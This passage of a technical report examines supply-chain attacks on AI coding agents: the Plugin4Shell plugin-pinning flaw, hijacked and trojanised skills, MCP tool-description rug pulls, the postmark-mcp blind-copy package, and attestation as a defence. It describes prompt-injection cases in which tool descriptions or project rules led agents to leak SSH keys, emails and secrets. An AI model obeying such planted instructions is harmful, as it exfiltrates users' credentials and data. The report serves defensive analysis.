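| Claude Code | Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 2.1.179 | Update |
| Codex | OpenAI fixed the flaw in version 0.146.0 | Update |
| GitHub Copilot | Microsoft, which owns GitHub, had released no fix | Install only plugins hosted on GitHub |
| Gemini CLI | Google retired the product and plans no fix | Remove the plugins or change to another agent |

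GitHub answered that its own hosting blocks branches and tags (names attached to one commit, usually to mark a release) that imitate commit identifiers, according to ilsoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI*. The researchers replied that Copilot also supports repositories hosted elsewhere. GitHub's rule protects plugins hosted on GitHub, but not internal plugins that a company keeps on its own Git server. The missing check takes about one line of code, so the rule is a weak reason to leave it out.

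Google advises Gemini CLI users to move to its newer agent, Antigravity, which has no plugin pinning of this kind, according to Help Net Security. Moving avoids the flaw, but an operator who wants to keep a plugin at a reviewed version then needs another way to do it.

Digital Matters' *Plugin4Shell* (2026), published on 6 October, lists the same two fixed versions. Microsoft may have fixed Copilot since then with little publicity, so operators should check its release notes before relying on a pin.

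An operator who froze the harness before the fix still has the flaw, which is one drawback of delaying updates. Claude Code's settings for a permitted version range can prevent any release older than 2.1.179 from starting. Updating may still leave existing plugins unchanged, because the check runs during download. To find out whether an earlier download installed the wrong files, the operator can fetch each plugin again on a separate machine, confirm its commit with the comparison above, and compare the files with the installed copy.

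### Hijacked skills

To exploit Plugin4Shell, an attacker has to control the repository behind a plugin that people already use. One way is to publish a useful plugin and alter it later. AIR tried the first step with its own malicious skill, which reached more than 26,000 agents before its removal. The other way is to take over a repository from its owner. In its SkillJacking research, AIR counted 925 skills "hijacked out from under their maintainers", affecting 134,000 agents.

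Those figures average about 145 agents per skill if each agent had only one of them, so most of the skills probably had few users. AIR's summary does not name the hijackers, and Help Net Security does not explain how AIR counted agents. If the number comes from downloads, it includes scanners and repeated installations, as with the first day's downloads of `react-codeshift`. A count of machines that contacted a server AIR controlled would be much stronger evidence.

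AIR also has a commercial interest in these numbers. It sells a plugin marketplace and a filter, and it says in its disclosure that customers using them were not affected. Some of its claims are exaggerated. It calls Plugin4Shell the first supply-chain vulnerability of the AI agent ecosystem, although the theft of Cline's npm token had shown seven months earlier that an attacker could tamper with the distribution of a coding agent. AIR also says the whole chain is "proven end to end". It has shown that people can take over repositories and that the pins could fail, but these were separate findings, the first about skills and the second about plugins with a pinned commit. The evidence that the flaw exists is much stronger than the evidence for its reach, because Anthropic and OpenAI both changed their products.

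### Skills that changed after installation

In August 2026, the security company Zenity Labs reported a campaign that needed no flaw in Git. The attackers copied existing skills and published them under similar names on skills.sh, a public skill registry owned by the cloud company Vercel. According to TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever*, the copies were harmless at first. After the copies had a fair number of downloads, the attackers added instructions for the agent to gather and send out login keys, cloud credentials and database passwords.

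One family of these skills had more than 1.7 million installations, but Zenity could not say how many people had lost data. Installations are not a count of victims, because one user can install a skill many times. The total presumably also includes installations from the harmless period, and some of those users may never have received the altered version.

If the agent had verified pins, a company that reviewed one of the copies in its first weeks and recorded the commit would have kept the harmless text. A later update would have required a new review, and a reviewer should notice a request to collect passwords in a skill for, say, formatting code. But a company that first installed the skill after the change would have pinned the malicious version.

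Vercel and Microsoft removed the skills that Zenity had identified, but users still have to delete their own copies, so an operator needs to know which machines have them. JFrog's *Stop Treating Coding Agent Plugins Like Settings* describes a product that keeps this record. The operator runs a private plugin repository from which developers install approved plugins, and the repository logs which machines fetched which version. JFrog is describing its own product, but an ordinary internal package server with good logs could provide the same list.

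A pin gives little protection if the review was poor, as a more recent campaign shows. AIR calls it TrojanPony and dates its start to July 2026. By 26 November, AIR had found the malware in 487 public repositories, according to ID.nl's *Honderden nepmodules voor Claude Code installeren wachtwoordsteler op Windows*. Hundreds of them were copies of known skills with a word such as "improved" added to the name. They mostly worked as users expected, but on Windows they also installed a program that steals passwords. One of the infected skills had passed checks by three automated security services. An operator who trusted those results and pinned the commit would have kept the malicious files, and their hash would have been correct.

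The malware also came with the genuine, digitally signed updater for the text editor Notepad++. The attackers placed an altered library file beside it, and Windows loaded that file when the updater started. An allowlist that checked only the program's signature would have let the updater run. A reviewer who compared every file with the official Notepad++ release would have found the altered library.

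Twenty of the repositories belonged to a legitimate developer whose access token the attackers had stolen. A verified pin from before the theft would have protected users of that developer's software from the malware.

### Three designs compared

The simplest design has no pin. Red Hat's guide says Claude Code plugins work this way, with neither version pinning nor a content hash for updates. Anyone who reinstalls a plugin gets whatever is on the repository's default branch at that moment. AIR, by contrast, describes marketplaces that do pin commits. Both accounts can be right if some marketplace entries name a commit and others name only a repository, so an operator has to read each plugin's entry.

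Red Hat advises plugin authors to publish releases under tags and direct users to a tag. This lets users choose a version, but someone with enough rights over the repository can move the tag to another commit. Red Hat therefore also recommends protecting tags and having a second person review every change. These measures depend on the author, and users can't enforce them.

In the second design, the marketplace records a commit and the agent confirms it after downloading. Claude Code and Codex should now do this. The agent checks only once, so if another program on the machine later edits the plugin, the agent will load the edited files the next time it starts. In NVIDIA's test on Codex, a malicious library made a similar change by writing to a file that the agent trusted.

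In the third design, the operator records a hash for every file in the plugin, and a program recomputes the hashes each time the agent loads the plugin. For `release-notes`, the script that starts the agent could compare the files' hashes with an approved list, as in the Codex setup script, and start the harness only if they match. The list and the script both have to be stored where neither the agent nor its plugins can write. An ordinary laptop can hash several hundred megabytes per second, so checking a five-megabyte plugin would take a few hundredths of a second.

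| Event | No pin | Commit, confirmed after download | Every file hashed at each load |
|---|---|---|---|
| The author adds harmful code after the review | The next installation or update receives it | The agent keeps the reviewed version | The agent keeps the reviewed version |
| The download contains files from another commit | Nobody notices | The agent refuses the plugin | The agent does not start |
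| A program edits the plugin on the disk | Nobody notices | Nobody notices before the next download | The agent does not start |
| The reviewers overlooked harmful code | It runs | It runs | It runs |
| A harmless new version appears | Users get it at once | Users wait for a review | Users wait for a review and new hashes |

Even with the third design, another program could alter a plugin's script after the agent loads the plugin and before the script runs, which may be an hour later. The operator can prevent this by making the plugin's folder read-only for the agent and everything it starts. A sealed image already works this way if the operator builds the reviewed plugin into it and turns off plugin updates.

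None of this controls what an unchanged plugin reads. Hookify, a plugin in Anthropic's official marketplace, took rules from files in the user's project and passed them to the model as trusted instructions. Red Hat reports that researchers at Pluto Security wrote five malicious rules that looked like ordinary project conventions. In tests with Claude Opus 4.6, all five made the model leak environment variables and local secrets. Anthropic closed the report, reasoning that a user who marks a project folder as trusted also trusts the instructions in it. Hookify's own files could all have matched their approved hashes during those tests. An operator could add the rule files to the list of hashes. This is practical for a project that rarely changes, but coding agents often work on projects where other people add files every day.

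## Tool servers run by someone else

An operator can hash a plugin because its files are on the operator's own machine. Many agents also use MCP servers that other companies run, where the operator has no files to check. The operator receives only a text description of each tool and, later, its results.

### How a server announces a tool

Suppose the accountants who use the `invoice-check` skill connect their agent to another company's currency converter. The harness sends the server a `tools/list` request, and the reply contains this entry:

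```
{
  "name": "convert_currency",
  "description": "Convert an amount at today's central bank rate",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "amount": {"type": "number"},
      "from": {"type": "string"},
      "to": {"type": "string"}
    },
    "required": ["amount", "from", "to"]
  }
}
```

The input schema defines the arguments the tool accepts. The harness adds the entry to the text the model reads, and the model uses it to decide when to call the tool and which arguments to send. An entry can also include a schema for the results and annotations about the tool's behaviour. *Tools* (2026), part of the official Model Context Protocol specification, tells clients not to trust annotations unless they trust the server.

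The current specification dates from 28 July 2026, and Model Context Protocol's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026) gives 30 March 2027 as the target for the next one. The current version allows a server's list of tools to change at any time. It recommends but does not require that the server send a notification of the change, so an owner who wants to hide a change can leave it out. Only harnesses that have opened a separate stream for such messages receive the notification. Each list also includes a limit on how long a harness may reuse it before asking again, which is five minutes in the specification's example.

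Many changes to a server's tool list are harmless. A participant in the Cursor forum thread *MCP* describes servers that offer only a login tool until the user logs in, and others that start with one tool for discovering the rest, which leaves more room in the model's context. The July revision still lets the list depend on the user's authorisation, but it no longer lets one request change the list as a side effect, which seems to rule out the second design.

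### Descriptions that change after approval

Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (1 April 2025) describes a "rug pull", in which a server's owner changes a tool's description after the user has approved the tool. This matters because the model may follow instructions in the new description.

Invariant Labs, a security company, demonstrated an attack using a tool named `add`. The tool's description contained instructions for the model to read the user's private SSH key and pass it along in an extra argument called `sidenote`. Cursor's agent followed them. Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but its dialog didn't show the full argument, so the user couldn't see the key.

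A second experiment connected the agent to a trusted email server and a malicious one. The description of the malicious server's `add` tool contained an instruction to send every email to the attacker, and the agent obeyed, even when the user had named another recipient. So an attacker doesn't need the agent to call the malicious tool. The descriptions in both experiments were malicious from the start, but a rug pull could introduce the same text after a reviewer had approved a harmless version.

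### The package postmark-mcp

In September 2025, the security company Koi reported what it called the first malicious MCP server in real use, an npm package named `postmark-mcp` that let agents send email through Postmark. Its publisher had copied Postmark's genuine server from GitHub. Version 1.0.16 added a single line, which sent a blind copy of every email to an address the publisher controlled. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, lists the same version. Postmark said that it had no connection with the package and had not published its MCP server on npm before the incident.

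The scale of the theft is uncertain. Koi reports 1,500 downloads a week and guesses that 20% were in active use. From this, it estimates that about 300 organisations were affected and 3,000 to 15,000 emails were copied a day. The Hacker News (2025) reports 1,643 downloads in total. It dates the first upload to 15 September and version 1.0.16 to 17 September, which doesn't fit Koi's account of users coming to trust the tool over months. As with Cline, the number of downloads probably overstates the number of victims.

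Koi writes that nothing else changed in version 1.0.16, so a check of the tool descriptions would have found no difference. A list of permitted domains would probably not have helped either, because the server sent the blind copies through Postmark, which it had to contact anyway.

Because the server ran on the user's machine, pinning could have protected people who had installed an earlier version. Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* (2025) dates Koi's report to 25 September, one day after a seven-day cooldown would have ended. A reviewer could have seen the extra line by comparing the new version with the previous one or with the genuine code on GitHub.

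### Comparing definitions by hash

The gateway that checks an agent's tool calls against written rules can also detect altered descriptions:

1. A reviewer reads the tool's complete definition, and the gateway stores its hash.
2. Whenever the server sends its list, the gateway computes the hash again.
3. If the two hashes match, the gateway passes the definition to the agent.
4. If they differ, or if the tool is new, the gateway withholds the tool until a reviewer has approved it.

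With the server's reply saved as `tools.json`, this command computes the hash for the currency tool:

```
jq -cS '.result.tools[] | select(.name == "convert_currency")' \
    tools.json | sha256sum
```

The option `-S` sorts the fields by name, so the hash stays the same if the server merely sends them in a different order.

Checking the tool list once per session could miss changes, because the list can change while the agent works. The July revision also removed sessions from the protocol, so the gateway should check every list it receives. It should check the copy meant for the agent, since one fetched with an administrator's credentials may differ.

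Gateways can now read a tool's name from the request's headers without opening the message body (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A gateway that reads only the headers can block a tool by name but can't read the tool's definition.

### Two designs and what tests exist

*Containing the Autonomous Operator*, the October 2026 design for agents on Kubernetes, includes this check. In one of its scenarios, the owner of an outside server changes a description months after approval, adding an instruction for the agent to read a secret and send it to the server as an argument. The gateway detects the new hash and quarantines the server. Even if the check failed, none of the agent's tools would return the secret.

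The gateway also rejects tools whose names are confusingly similar to those on another server. That rule would not have stopped Invariant Labs' second experiment, because `add` and the email tool had different names. The hash would catch such instructions only if the owner added them after approval.

*ETDI* (Bhatt, Narajala and Habler, 2025) proposes an extension to the protocol. The tool's provider gives each definition a version number and a list of permissions, then signs it. The harness verifies the signature and compares the definition with the one the user approved. If the content has changed under the same version number, the harness reports tampering and asks for approval again. It also asks for approval of every new version.

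The signature would expose an impostor, but it would not prevent a harmful definition from being signed by the real provider or by someone who stole the provider's key. ETDI also needs providers and harnesses to adopt it, whereas an operator can add a gateway without the server owner's help. According to *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, MCP still has no standard for signed, versioned tool definitions.

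Neither paper gives strong evidence that its design works in practice. The Kubernetes paper reports no measurements. Bhatt and colleagues link to a demonstration implementation, which suggests the design is feasible but doesn't show how many attacks it would stop.

*MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (2026) recommends the same comparison of hashes and adds that it needs little computing power. The study also tested automatic checks of descriptions at registration. One check, which flags descriptions longer than 500 characters, rejected only 2 of 45 attack scenarios and flagged 3 of 125 harmless descriptions. A reviewer who relied on length alone would approve most of the malicious tools, and the gateway would then preserve them.

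### What current products check

*SchemaCaps* (2026) examined what happens when an approved tool starts to accept more arguments. It infers from the documentation, as of the end of September, that Claude Code 2.1.285 uses the new definition without prompting the user, because its permission rules match only the tool's name. Cursor 3.22 also lists permitted tools by name, and its documentation doesn't explain how it handles changes.

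The study tested the scanner mcp-scan 0.4.2. This version hashes only a tool's description, so it gave no warning when only the schema changed. The currency converter's owner could add an optional argument named `invoice_text` without triggering a warning, as long as the description stayed the same, and the model might then fill in that argument.

Hashing a tool's complete definition means more work for reviewers. In the updates that *SchemaCaps* studied, this would have required 2,004 new approvals, 807 of them (40%) for changes to only a description or title. Pinning just the input schema would have reduced the total to 1,197.

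Some schema changes only restrict a tool, and an operator could accept those automatically. If [S] is the set of calls that the old schema permits and [S′] the set that the new one permits, the gateway asks for approval unless

[S′] ⊆ [S].

This rule required 693 approvals, but it accepted without approval 7 changes that *SchemaCaps* classified as increasing the tool's power and 15 that *SchemaCaps* could not classify. The rule checks which arguments a call may contain but not the values that take effect. Those values could presumably change if the owner altered a default.

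*SchemaCaps* proposes a more careful analysis of schemas, but it also ignores descriptions, so for an agent it misses the text Invariant Labs used in its attacks. An operator who connects to strangers' servers should probably accept the extra reviews, and can limit the number of reviews by connecting to fewer servers.

### An unchanged description with different code behind it

Suppose the gateway has approved `convert_currency` and stored its hash. The accountants convert an invoice for 10,000 dollars at a rate of 0.90, and the tool returns 9,000 euros. A month later, the server's owner changes the program to add 1% to every result. At the same rate, the same invoice now comes to 9,090 euros.

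The name, description and schema are identical, so the hash still matches. With H for the hash function, d₀ for the approved definition and dₜ for the definition at time t, the gateway checks that

H(dₜ) = H(d₀).

This equation does not include the server's code. The owner could also start recording every amount, or have the tool return a sentence telling the agent to send more data. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists this kind of hidden code change alongside compromised dependencies and gradual changes in behaviour.

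ETDI goes a little further by letting a definition include a hash of the tool's API contract, a formal description of the requests and responses that the underlying service supports. The check would detect a new type of request but not a 1% surcharge, which leaves the contract unchanged. It might also miss an attack that Bhatt and colleagues describe, in which a wallpaper tool keeps its name and version number while new code searches the user's documents for financial data and uploads them.

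The current protocol also lets a server respond to a call by requesting more information from the user. The specification gives the example of a GitHub username. The currency converter could start requesting bank details this way without changing its hash, because the definition doesn't include such requests. A gateway can block them for any tool that didn't need them when it was approved.

The gateway can also restrict the results. If the approved definition has an output schema that allows only a single number, the gateway can reject any result that doesn't fit. The specification recommends that servers repeat structured results as ordinary text for older clients, so the gateway should discard that text and pass on only the number. This keeps instructions out of the result, but it doesn't catch a wrong number, such as 9,090 instead of 9,000, because both fit the schema.

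### Local servers and remote ones

A local MCP server is a program on the operator's machine, so its code can go into the sealed image like any other package. Building a reviewed version into the image also avoids the unpinned `npx` commands that users often run to start these servers. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* runs its tool servers from signed images pinned by digest and accepts images only from an internal registry.

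Local code may still depend on a remote service. For example, a local currency server may run approved code but request its rates from a bank's website, so the bank controls the rates.

With a remote server, the operator can normally fix only the interface. The server can state its name and version with each result, but the Python documentation from Model Context Protocol calls this information "self-reported and unverified". An operator would need remote attestation, which Apple's Private Cloud Compute offers, to get proof of the software on the other machine. Without it, the operator of the currency tool has these options:

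| Option | What the operator gains | What remains uncertain |
|---|---|---|
| Contract | Notice of changes and a claim for damages | Whether the owner keeps the agreement |
| Signed releases | A chance to review each version | Whether the server runs that version |
| Logged responses | Evidence of what the tool returned | What the server did with the data |
| Local copy | Control over the code | Whether outside data is correct |
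| Exclusion | No exposure to the server | Nothing, but the agent loses the tool |

A contract is most useful with a company that has a reputation to protect and money to pay damages. The contract could require 30 days' notice before any change to the code and let the operator's auditors inspect the server. It would offer little protection against an anonymous developer or an attacker who has broken into the server.

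Signed releases help most when the operator can also run them. If the owner publishes the converter's source code, auditors can read each version, but the public server may still run different code. The operator can remove that doubt by installing the signed release locally.

The operator has to arrange the logging, because MCP doesn't require any record of tool calls (*ChainWatch*, 2026). The gateway can save each request and response with the time and a hash of the tool's definition. It can also compare the converter's rate with a second source and stop the call if the two differ by more than, say, 0.5%, which would catch the 1% surcharge immediately. Many tools have no second source to compare against. A server that summarises legal documents, for example, could leave out a clause, and no simple calculation would reveal it.

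The log can't show whether the converter's owner keeps the invoice amounts. The accountants can avoid sending the amounts by always asking for the value of one dollar and multiplying it themselves.

For this task, the operator could work without the remote tool. A person or a scheduled program could download the central bank's table of rates each morning, check it for implausible changes and place it in the agent's read-only input folder. The conversion would then need only a few lines of approved code.

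Operators often can't make a local copy of a service such as a bug tracker or a customer database, because the data exists only on the provider's system. They can still limit what the agent sends to the service, give the agent read-only credentials and require a person to approve changes. If a wrong answer or a leak would do serious harm even with those limits, operators should not give the agent access to the server.

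## Apple's Private Cloud Compute and software images outsiders can check

Remote attestation can give an operator hardware-signed evidence of which software someone else's server has started. Apple uses it in Private Cloud Compute (PCC), the servers that handle requests too demanding for the AI model on an iPhone, iPad or Mac.

PCC serves AI models. It is not a general tool environment for agents, and customers can't install their own programs or containers on it. It is relevant here because Apple has publicly documented how it links a software image outsiders can examine to the remote machines running that image.

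### From a signed image to the user's phone

Suppose someone asks an iPhone to summarise a long email, which is one of the tasks that PCC handles. Before the phone sends the email, it checks what the server is running. Apple's *Private Cloud Compute*, which introduced the design, describes the steps behind this check:

1. Apple builds a system image and signs a list of all the code that may run on a server. The Secure Enclave, a separate security processor in Apple's chips, loads the list, and nobody can change it while the server runs.
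2. Apple leaves remote shells and debugging tools out of the image, so its own administrators can't log in and run commands. The server also can't compile or load new code after it starts.
3. At start-up, the server measures its software, which means that it computes hashes of what it loads.
4. The server produces an attestation, a statement of these measurements signed with a key that the hardware protects.
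5. Apple publishes the measurements of every release in an append-only log, a public record to which it can add entries but from which it can't remove any unnoticed.
6. The phone looks for the server's measurements in the log. If they are there, it encrypts the request so that only approved servers can read it.

Apple uses a similar procedure when an employer wants to verify a staff phone or computer. The hardware stores the start-up hashes in its own registers, and the Secure Enclave includes them in the attestation together with a public key. In simplified form, with m for the measurement and P for the public key,

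attestation = Sign(m, P).

The signed statement has to include the key. Otherwise an attacker could show the phone a genuine attestation from one server and have the phone encrypt the email for another.

The phone sends data only if the signature is valid and m ∈ L, where L is the set of measurements in the log. L has a similar role to the approved set A, which contains software that auditors have examined. But L contains whatever Apple has published, so it can include a release that nobody outside Apple has looked at yet.

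### How a log exposes a secret release

A log can be made append-only with the same hash functions that identify files. In the simplest version, each new entry produces a summary of the whole log so far. With mₙ for the measurement of release number n and rₙ for the summary after it,

rₙ = H(rₙ₋₁, mₙ).

If someone deletes or alters release 12, the summary changes at that point and at every later one. Anyone who saved an old summary can see that the new log doesn't continue from it. Large logs usually arrange the hashes in a tree, so a phone can confirm one entry without downloading the rest. In a log of a million entries, about 20 hashes are enough, because 2²⁰ is roughly a million.

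Suppose a court ordered Apple to run a version of the software that copies one customer's requests. Apple would have four options:

| What Apple could try | Result |
|---|---|
| Run the version without logging it | Phones refuse to send it data |
| Log it like any other release | Anyone who follows the log sees a new entry and expects an image to go with it |
| Log it and delete the entry afterwards | The log no longer matches the summaries that others have saved |
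| Show the customer's phone a different log | The phone's summary differs from everyone else's, but somebody has to compare them |

The last option is the hardest to detect. Users can review a record of the server software on their own devices, but few are likely to compare it with the public log.

The design also makes it difficult to single out one customer. Requests pass through another company's relay, which hides the sender's IP address from Apple, and the servers that distribute the requests receive nothing that identifies the user. To reach one person's data, an attacker would probably have to run the altered software on many servers, where more people could notice it.

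The log doesn't stop Apple from publishing a harmful release, and outsiders may have to wait to examine one. Apple promises to publish each image within 90 days of its log entry, or sooner if the relevant software updates become available first. A release logged on 1 March could process emails until 30 May before researchers received its image. This is the reverse of a dependency cooldown, in which users wait while others inspect the software. Apple could have phones reject any release whose image is not yet public, but its published check requires only the log entry.

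### What researchers can examine

Apple's *Security research on Private Cloud Compute* describes the main resource the company provides, a virtual research environment. This set of tools runs PCC's server software in a virtual machine on a Mac with an Apple chip and at least 16 GB of memory. Researchers can use it to check the log's consistency, download the programs in each release, start a release and send requests to demonstration models. They can also modify the software and watch how it behaves. Apple adapts the start-up process and the kernel for the virtual machine, but the programs above the kernel run as they do on a real server.

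Apple also publishes the source code of some security-critical components. One creates and checks attestations, another runs on the user's device and enforces the log check, and a third filters the logs that a server can send out. Apple releases the other programs only in compiled form.

Apple pays researchers up to $1,000,000 for reporting a remote attack that runs arbitrary code with arbitrary permissions, and up to $100,000 for reporting a way to run unattested code from a privileged position in the network. The second reward covers a direct failure of the guarantee, since the server would be running software not listed in its attestation.

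An auditor with these materials can confirm that a published image matches a log entry. *Unlocking Apple's Private Cloud Compute* (Dittmar, Stephan and colleagues, 2026) reports that linking the image to its source code is much harder, because Apple doesn't publish all the source and its builds aren't reproducible. The compiled programs also lack symbols, the function and variable names that would help a reader navigate the code.

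### Two outside investigations

Dittmar and colleagues, from the Hasso Plattner Institute and TU Darmstadt, examined the part of the system that runs on the user's device. This part is important to check because Apple also writes the program that determines whether to trust an Apple server. The researchers reverse-engineered the software on a Mac and an iPhone and found that it follows the published protocol, including a step that validates the server's attestation.

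The researchers then tested how the live servers handle the tokens that authorise a request. Each device has a long-lived token, which proves that it may use PCC, and a supply of one-time tokens for individual requests. The researchers could use the same one-time token between two and five times. They also overwrote the signature on a long-lived token with zeros, and the server still answered, although Apple's published source code contains a check for that signature.

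Neither fault gave outsiders access, because each request still needed a valid one-time token. The missing signature check matters more for an audit, because a reviewer who read only the source code would have concluded that the servers reject tokens without a valid signature. Dittmar and colleagues write that the check "does not seem to be activated", but they do not establish why. One possible reason is a setting that Apple can change without changing the program. In their conference slides, they report that Apple responded by clarifying its documentation but left the protocol and the checks unchanged.

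The other investigation concerned the server. Sentry's *Beyond Prompt Injection* (2026) describes a flaw for which Apple paid the researcher Drinor Selmanaj $150,000. Selmanaj founded Sentry, a security company unrelated to the error-reporting service of the same name. Belfiore (2026), in *Il reçoit 150 000 dollars pour avoir réussi à hacker Apple Private*, explains that a faulty check at start-up let him write files to a server with the system's highest privileges and redirect data about AI requests to his own machine.

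Selmanaj worked on research servers, and the tampered server gave the same attestation result as a clean one, so a phone that checked it correctly would not have detected the tampering. The matching results show that a start-up measurement may not cover every file and setting that affects a server's behaviour. Apple has fixed the flaw, and Belfiore reports that it did not affect the servers that handle customers' requests.

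Apple's security guide describes some of these outside influences. ConductAtlas (2026), a website that tracks changes to companies' policies, recorded a revision of 7 July 2026 in which Apple added a much longer list of contents. The list includes settings that Apple can change while a server is running and files that it distributes to servers from the cloud. An auditor would have to examine the permitted values of those settings as well as the software image.

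### Trust in the hardware and in Apple

Every step of the verification depends on Apple, which designs the chips, signs the permitted code, certifies the servers' keys, runs the log and writes the software on the phone. If Apple certified a key held outside a real Secure Enclave, whoever had the key could sign an attestation for any release in the log while running different software. Trail of Bits' *PCC* (2024), a security company's review of the original announcement, noted that Apple effectively owns the attestation keys.

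Apple tries to make this kind of fraud difficult. It takes high-resolution images of a server's components during manufacture, seals the server and activates a switch that detects tampering. At the data centre, several teams check the server again while an observer from outside the company watches, and only then does Apple certify the server's key. Apple has also commissioned an independent audit of its controls over this process. Such an audit can give outsiders some confidence that Apple certifies only genuine servers, but it does not cover the software those servers run.

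Apple's threat model includes an attacker with physical access to a server who can defeat some of its hardware protection. To limit the damage, the phone encrypts each request so that only a small group of servers can decrypt it. Researchers published attacks on attestation hardware in 2025 and 2026, so a hardware signature is strong evidence of what a machine runs but not proof.

In June 2026, Apple extended PCC to Google's data centres for its most demanding requests. There the chain relies on Intel processors, NVIDIA graphics chips and Google's Titan security chip. Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute* describes two additional protections. The first is an append-only ledger of all the Google hardware in the system, which works like the software log. The second is that attestation depends on at least two independent vendors for any component that could leak user data if compromised,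 so a single stolen signing key should not be enough to forge it.

The move spreads trust across more companies, but Apple still decides which software the phones accept. Apple also planned to phase in the full protections during a summer preview, so an auditor who examined the system in June might have found weaker protection than the finished design provides.

According to Apple's *Privacy and Security Group Lab* (2026), an app may send a request to PCC or to another company's model, such as one from Anthropic, but PCC's guarantees don't cover the outside model.

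### The same chain for an agent's tools

PCC now runs some agents. The contents list that ConductAtlas recorded includes a "PCC Agent", which coordinates calls to tools on several servers, and a "Multi-Turn Agent", which keeps a limited amount of information between requests in a conversation. Both run Apple's workflows with Apple's tools, so a company that wanted the same evidence for its own agent would have to build the chain itself.

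The spreadsheet agent already has some of it:

| Link | Apple's servers | The spreadsheet agent's container |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed software | Signed list of permitted code | Sealed image with a digest |
| No administrator access | No remote shell | Anyone who controls the host can use `docker exec` |
| Measurement | Hashes at each start | Docker verifies the digest when it downloads the image |
| Signed statement | Signature from a hardware-protected key | None from the hardware |
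| Record of releases | Public append-only log | A signed `release.txt` for each image |
| Check before sending data | The user's device, for every server | The operator, before starting the container |

The largest change would be to `docker exec`, which the harness currently uses to send commands to the container. It gives whoever runs the host the kind of access that Apple removed from its servers. The operator could instead put the container in a virtual machine with hardware attestation, where a small program would accept only the approved tool calls from the harness.

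The harness would then make the phone's check at the start of each session:

```
challenge = new random number
reply = ask the machine for an attestation that includes challenge
stop unless the hardware vendor's signature is valid
stop unless reply contains challenge
stop unless reply.measurement is in A
encrypt all files and tool calls for reply.public_key
```

The random number prevents a machine from reusing an attestation it recorded before someone changed its software. The fifth line uses the auditors' set A instead of the whole log because the operator can delete an old measurement from A, while an append-only log keeps every past release, including those with known vulnerabilities.

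If the operator uses the container only for internal work, A is enough and a public log adds little. The log becomes useful when a provider runs the same container for many customers, who could then check that they all receive the same software. The provider would also have to publish the images, since customers can't tell from a hash what the software contains.

Attestation would not make it safe to install software during a task. The measurement describes the machine at start-up, so if the agent later ran `pip install`, a fresh attestation could still show the approved value. The image itself has to block new programs, as the sealed container does. Attestation also would not cover scripts the agent writes later, so the chain suits an agent with a few typed tools much better than a coding agent.

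No provider of tool containers for agents appears to offer the whole chain. The hosted environments for Codex and Claude don't give customers a digest of the running image to compare with an attestation. Google's Private AI Compute is similar to PCC, but it too serves models rather than hosting tool containers. For its first release, Google relied on an outside auditor's review of the design and left further attestation for later.

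Operators can buy some of the parts needed for a similar system. Apple names Intel SGX and AWS Nitro as existing mechanisms for checking that a published image matches a running machine. With Nitro, a company could run the spreadsheet tools in an enclave, an isolated virtual machine on Amazon's servers, and have the harness check the enclave's measurement before sending any data. The company would have to write that check and maintain the list of approved measurements itself. It would also depend on Amazon's hardware and keys, as an iPhone user depends on Apple's.
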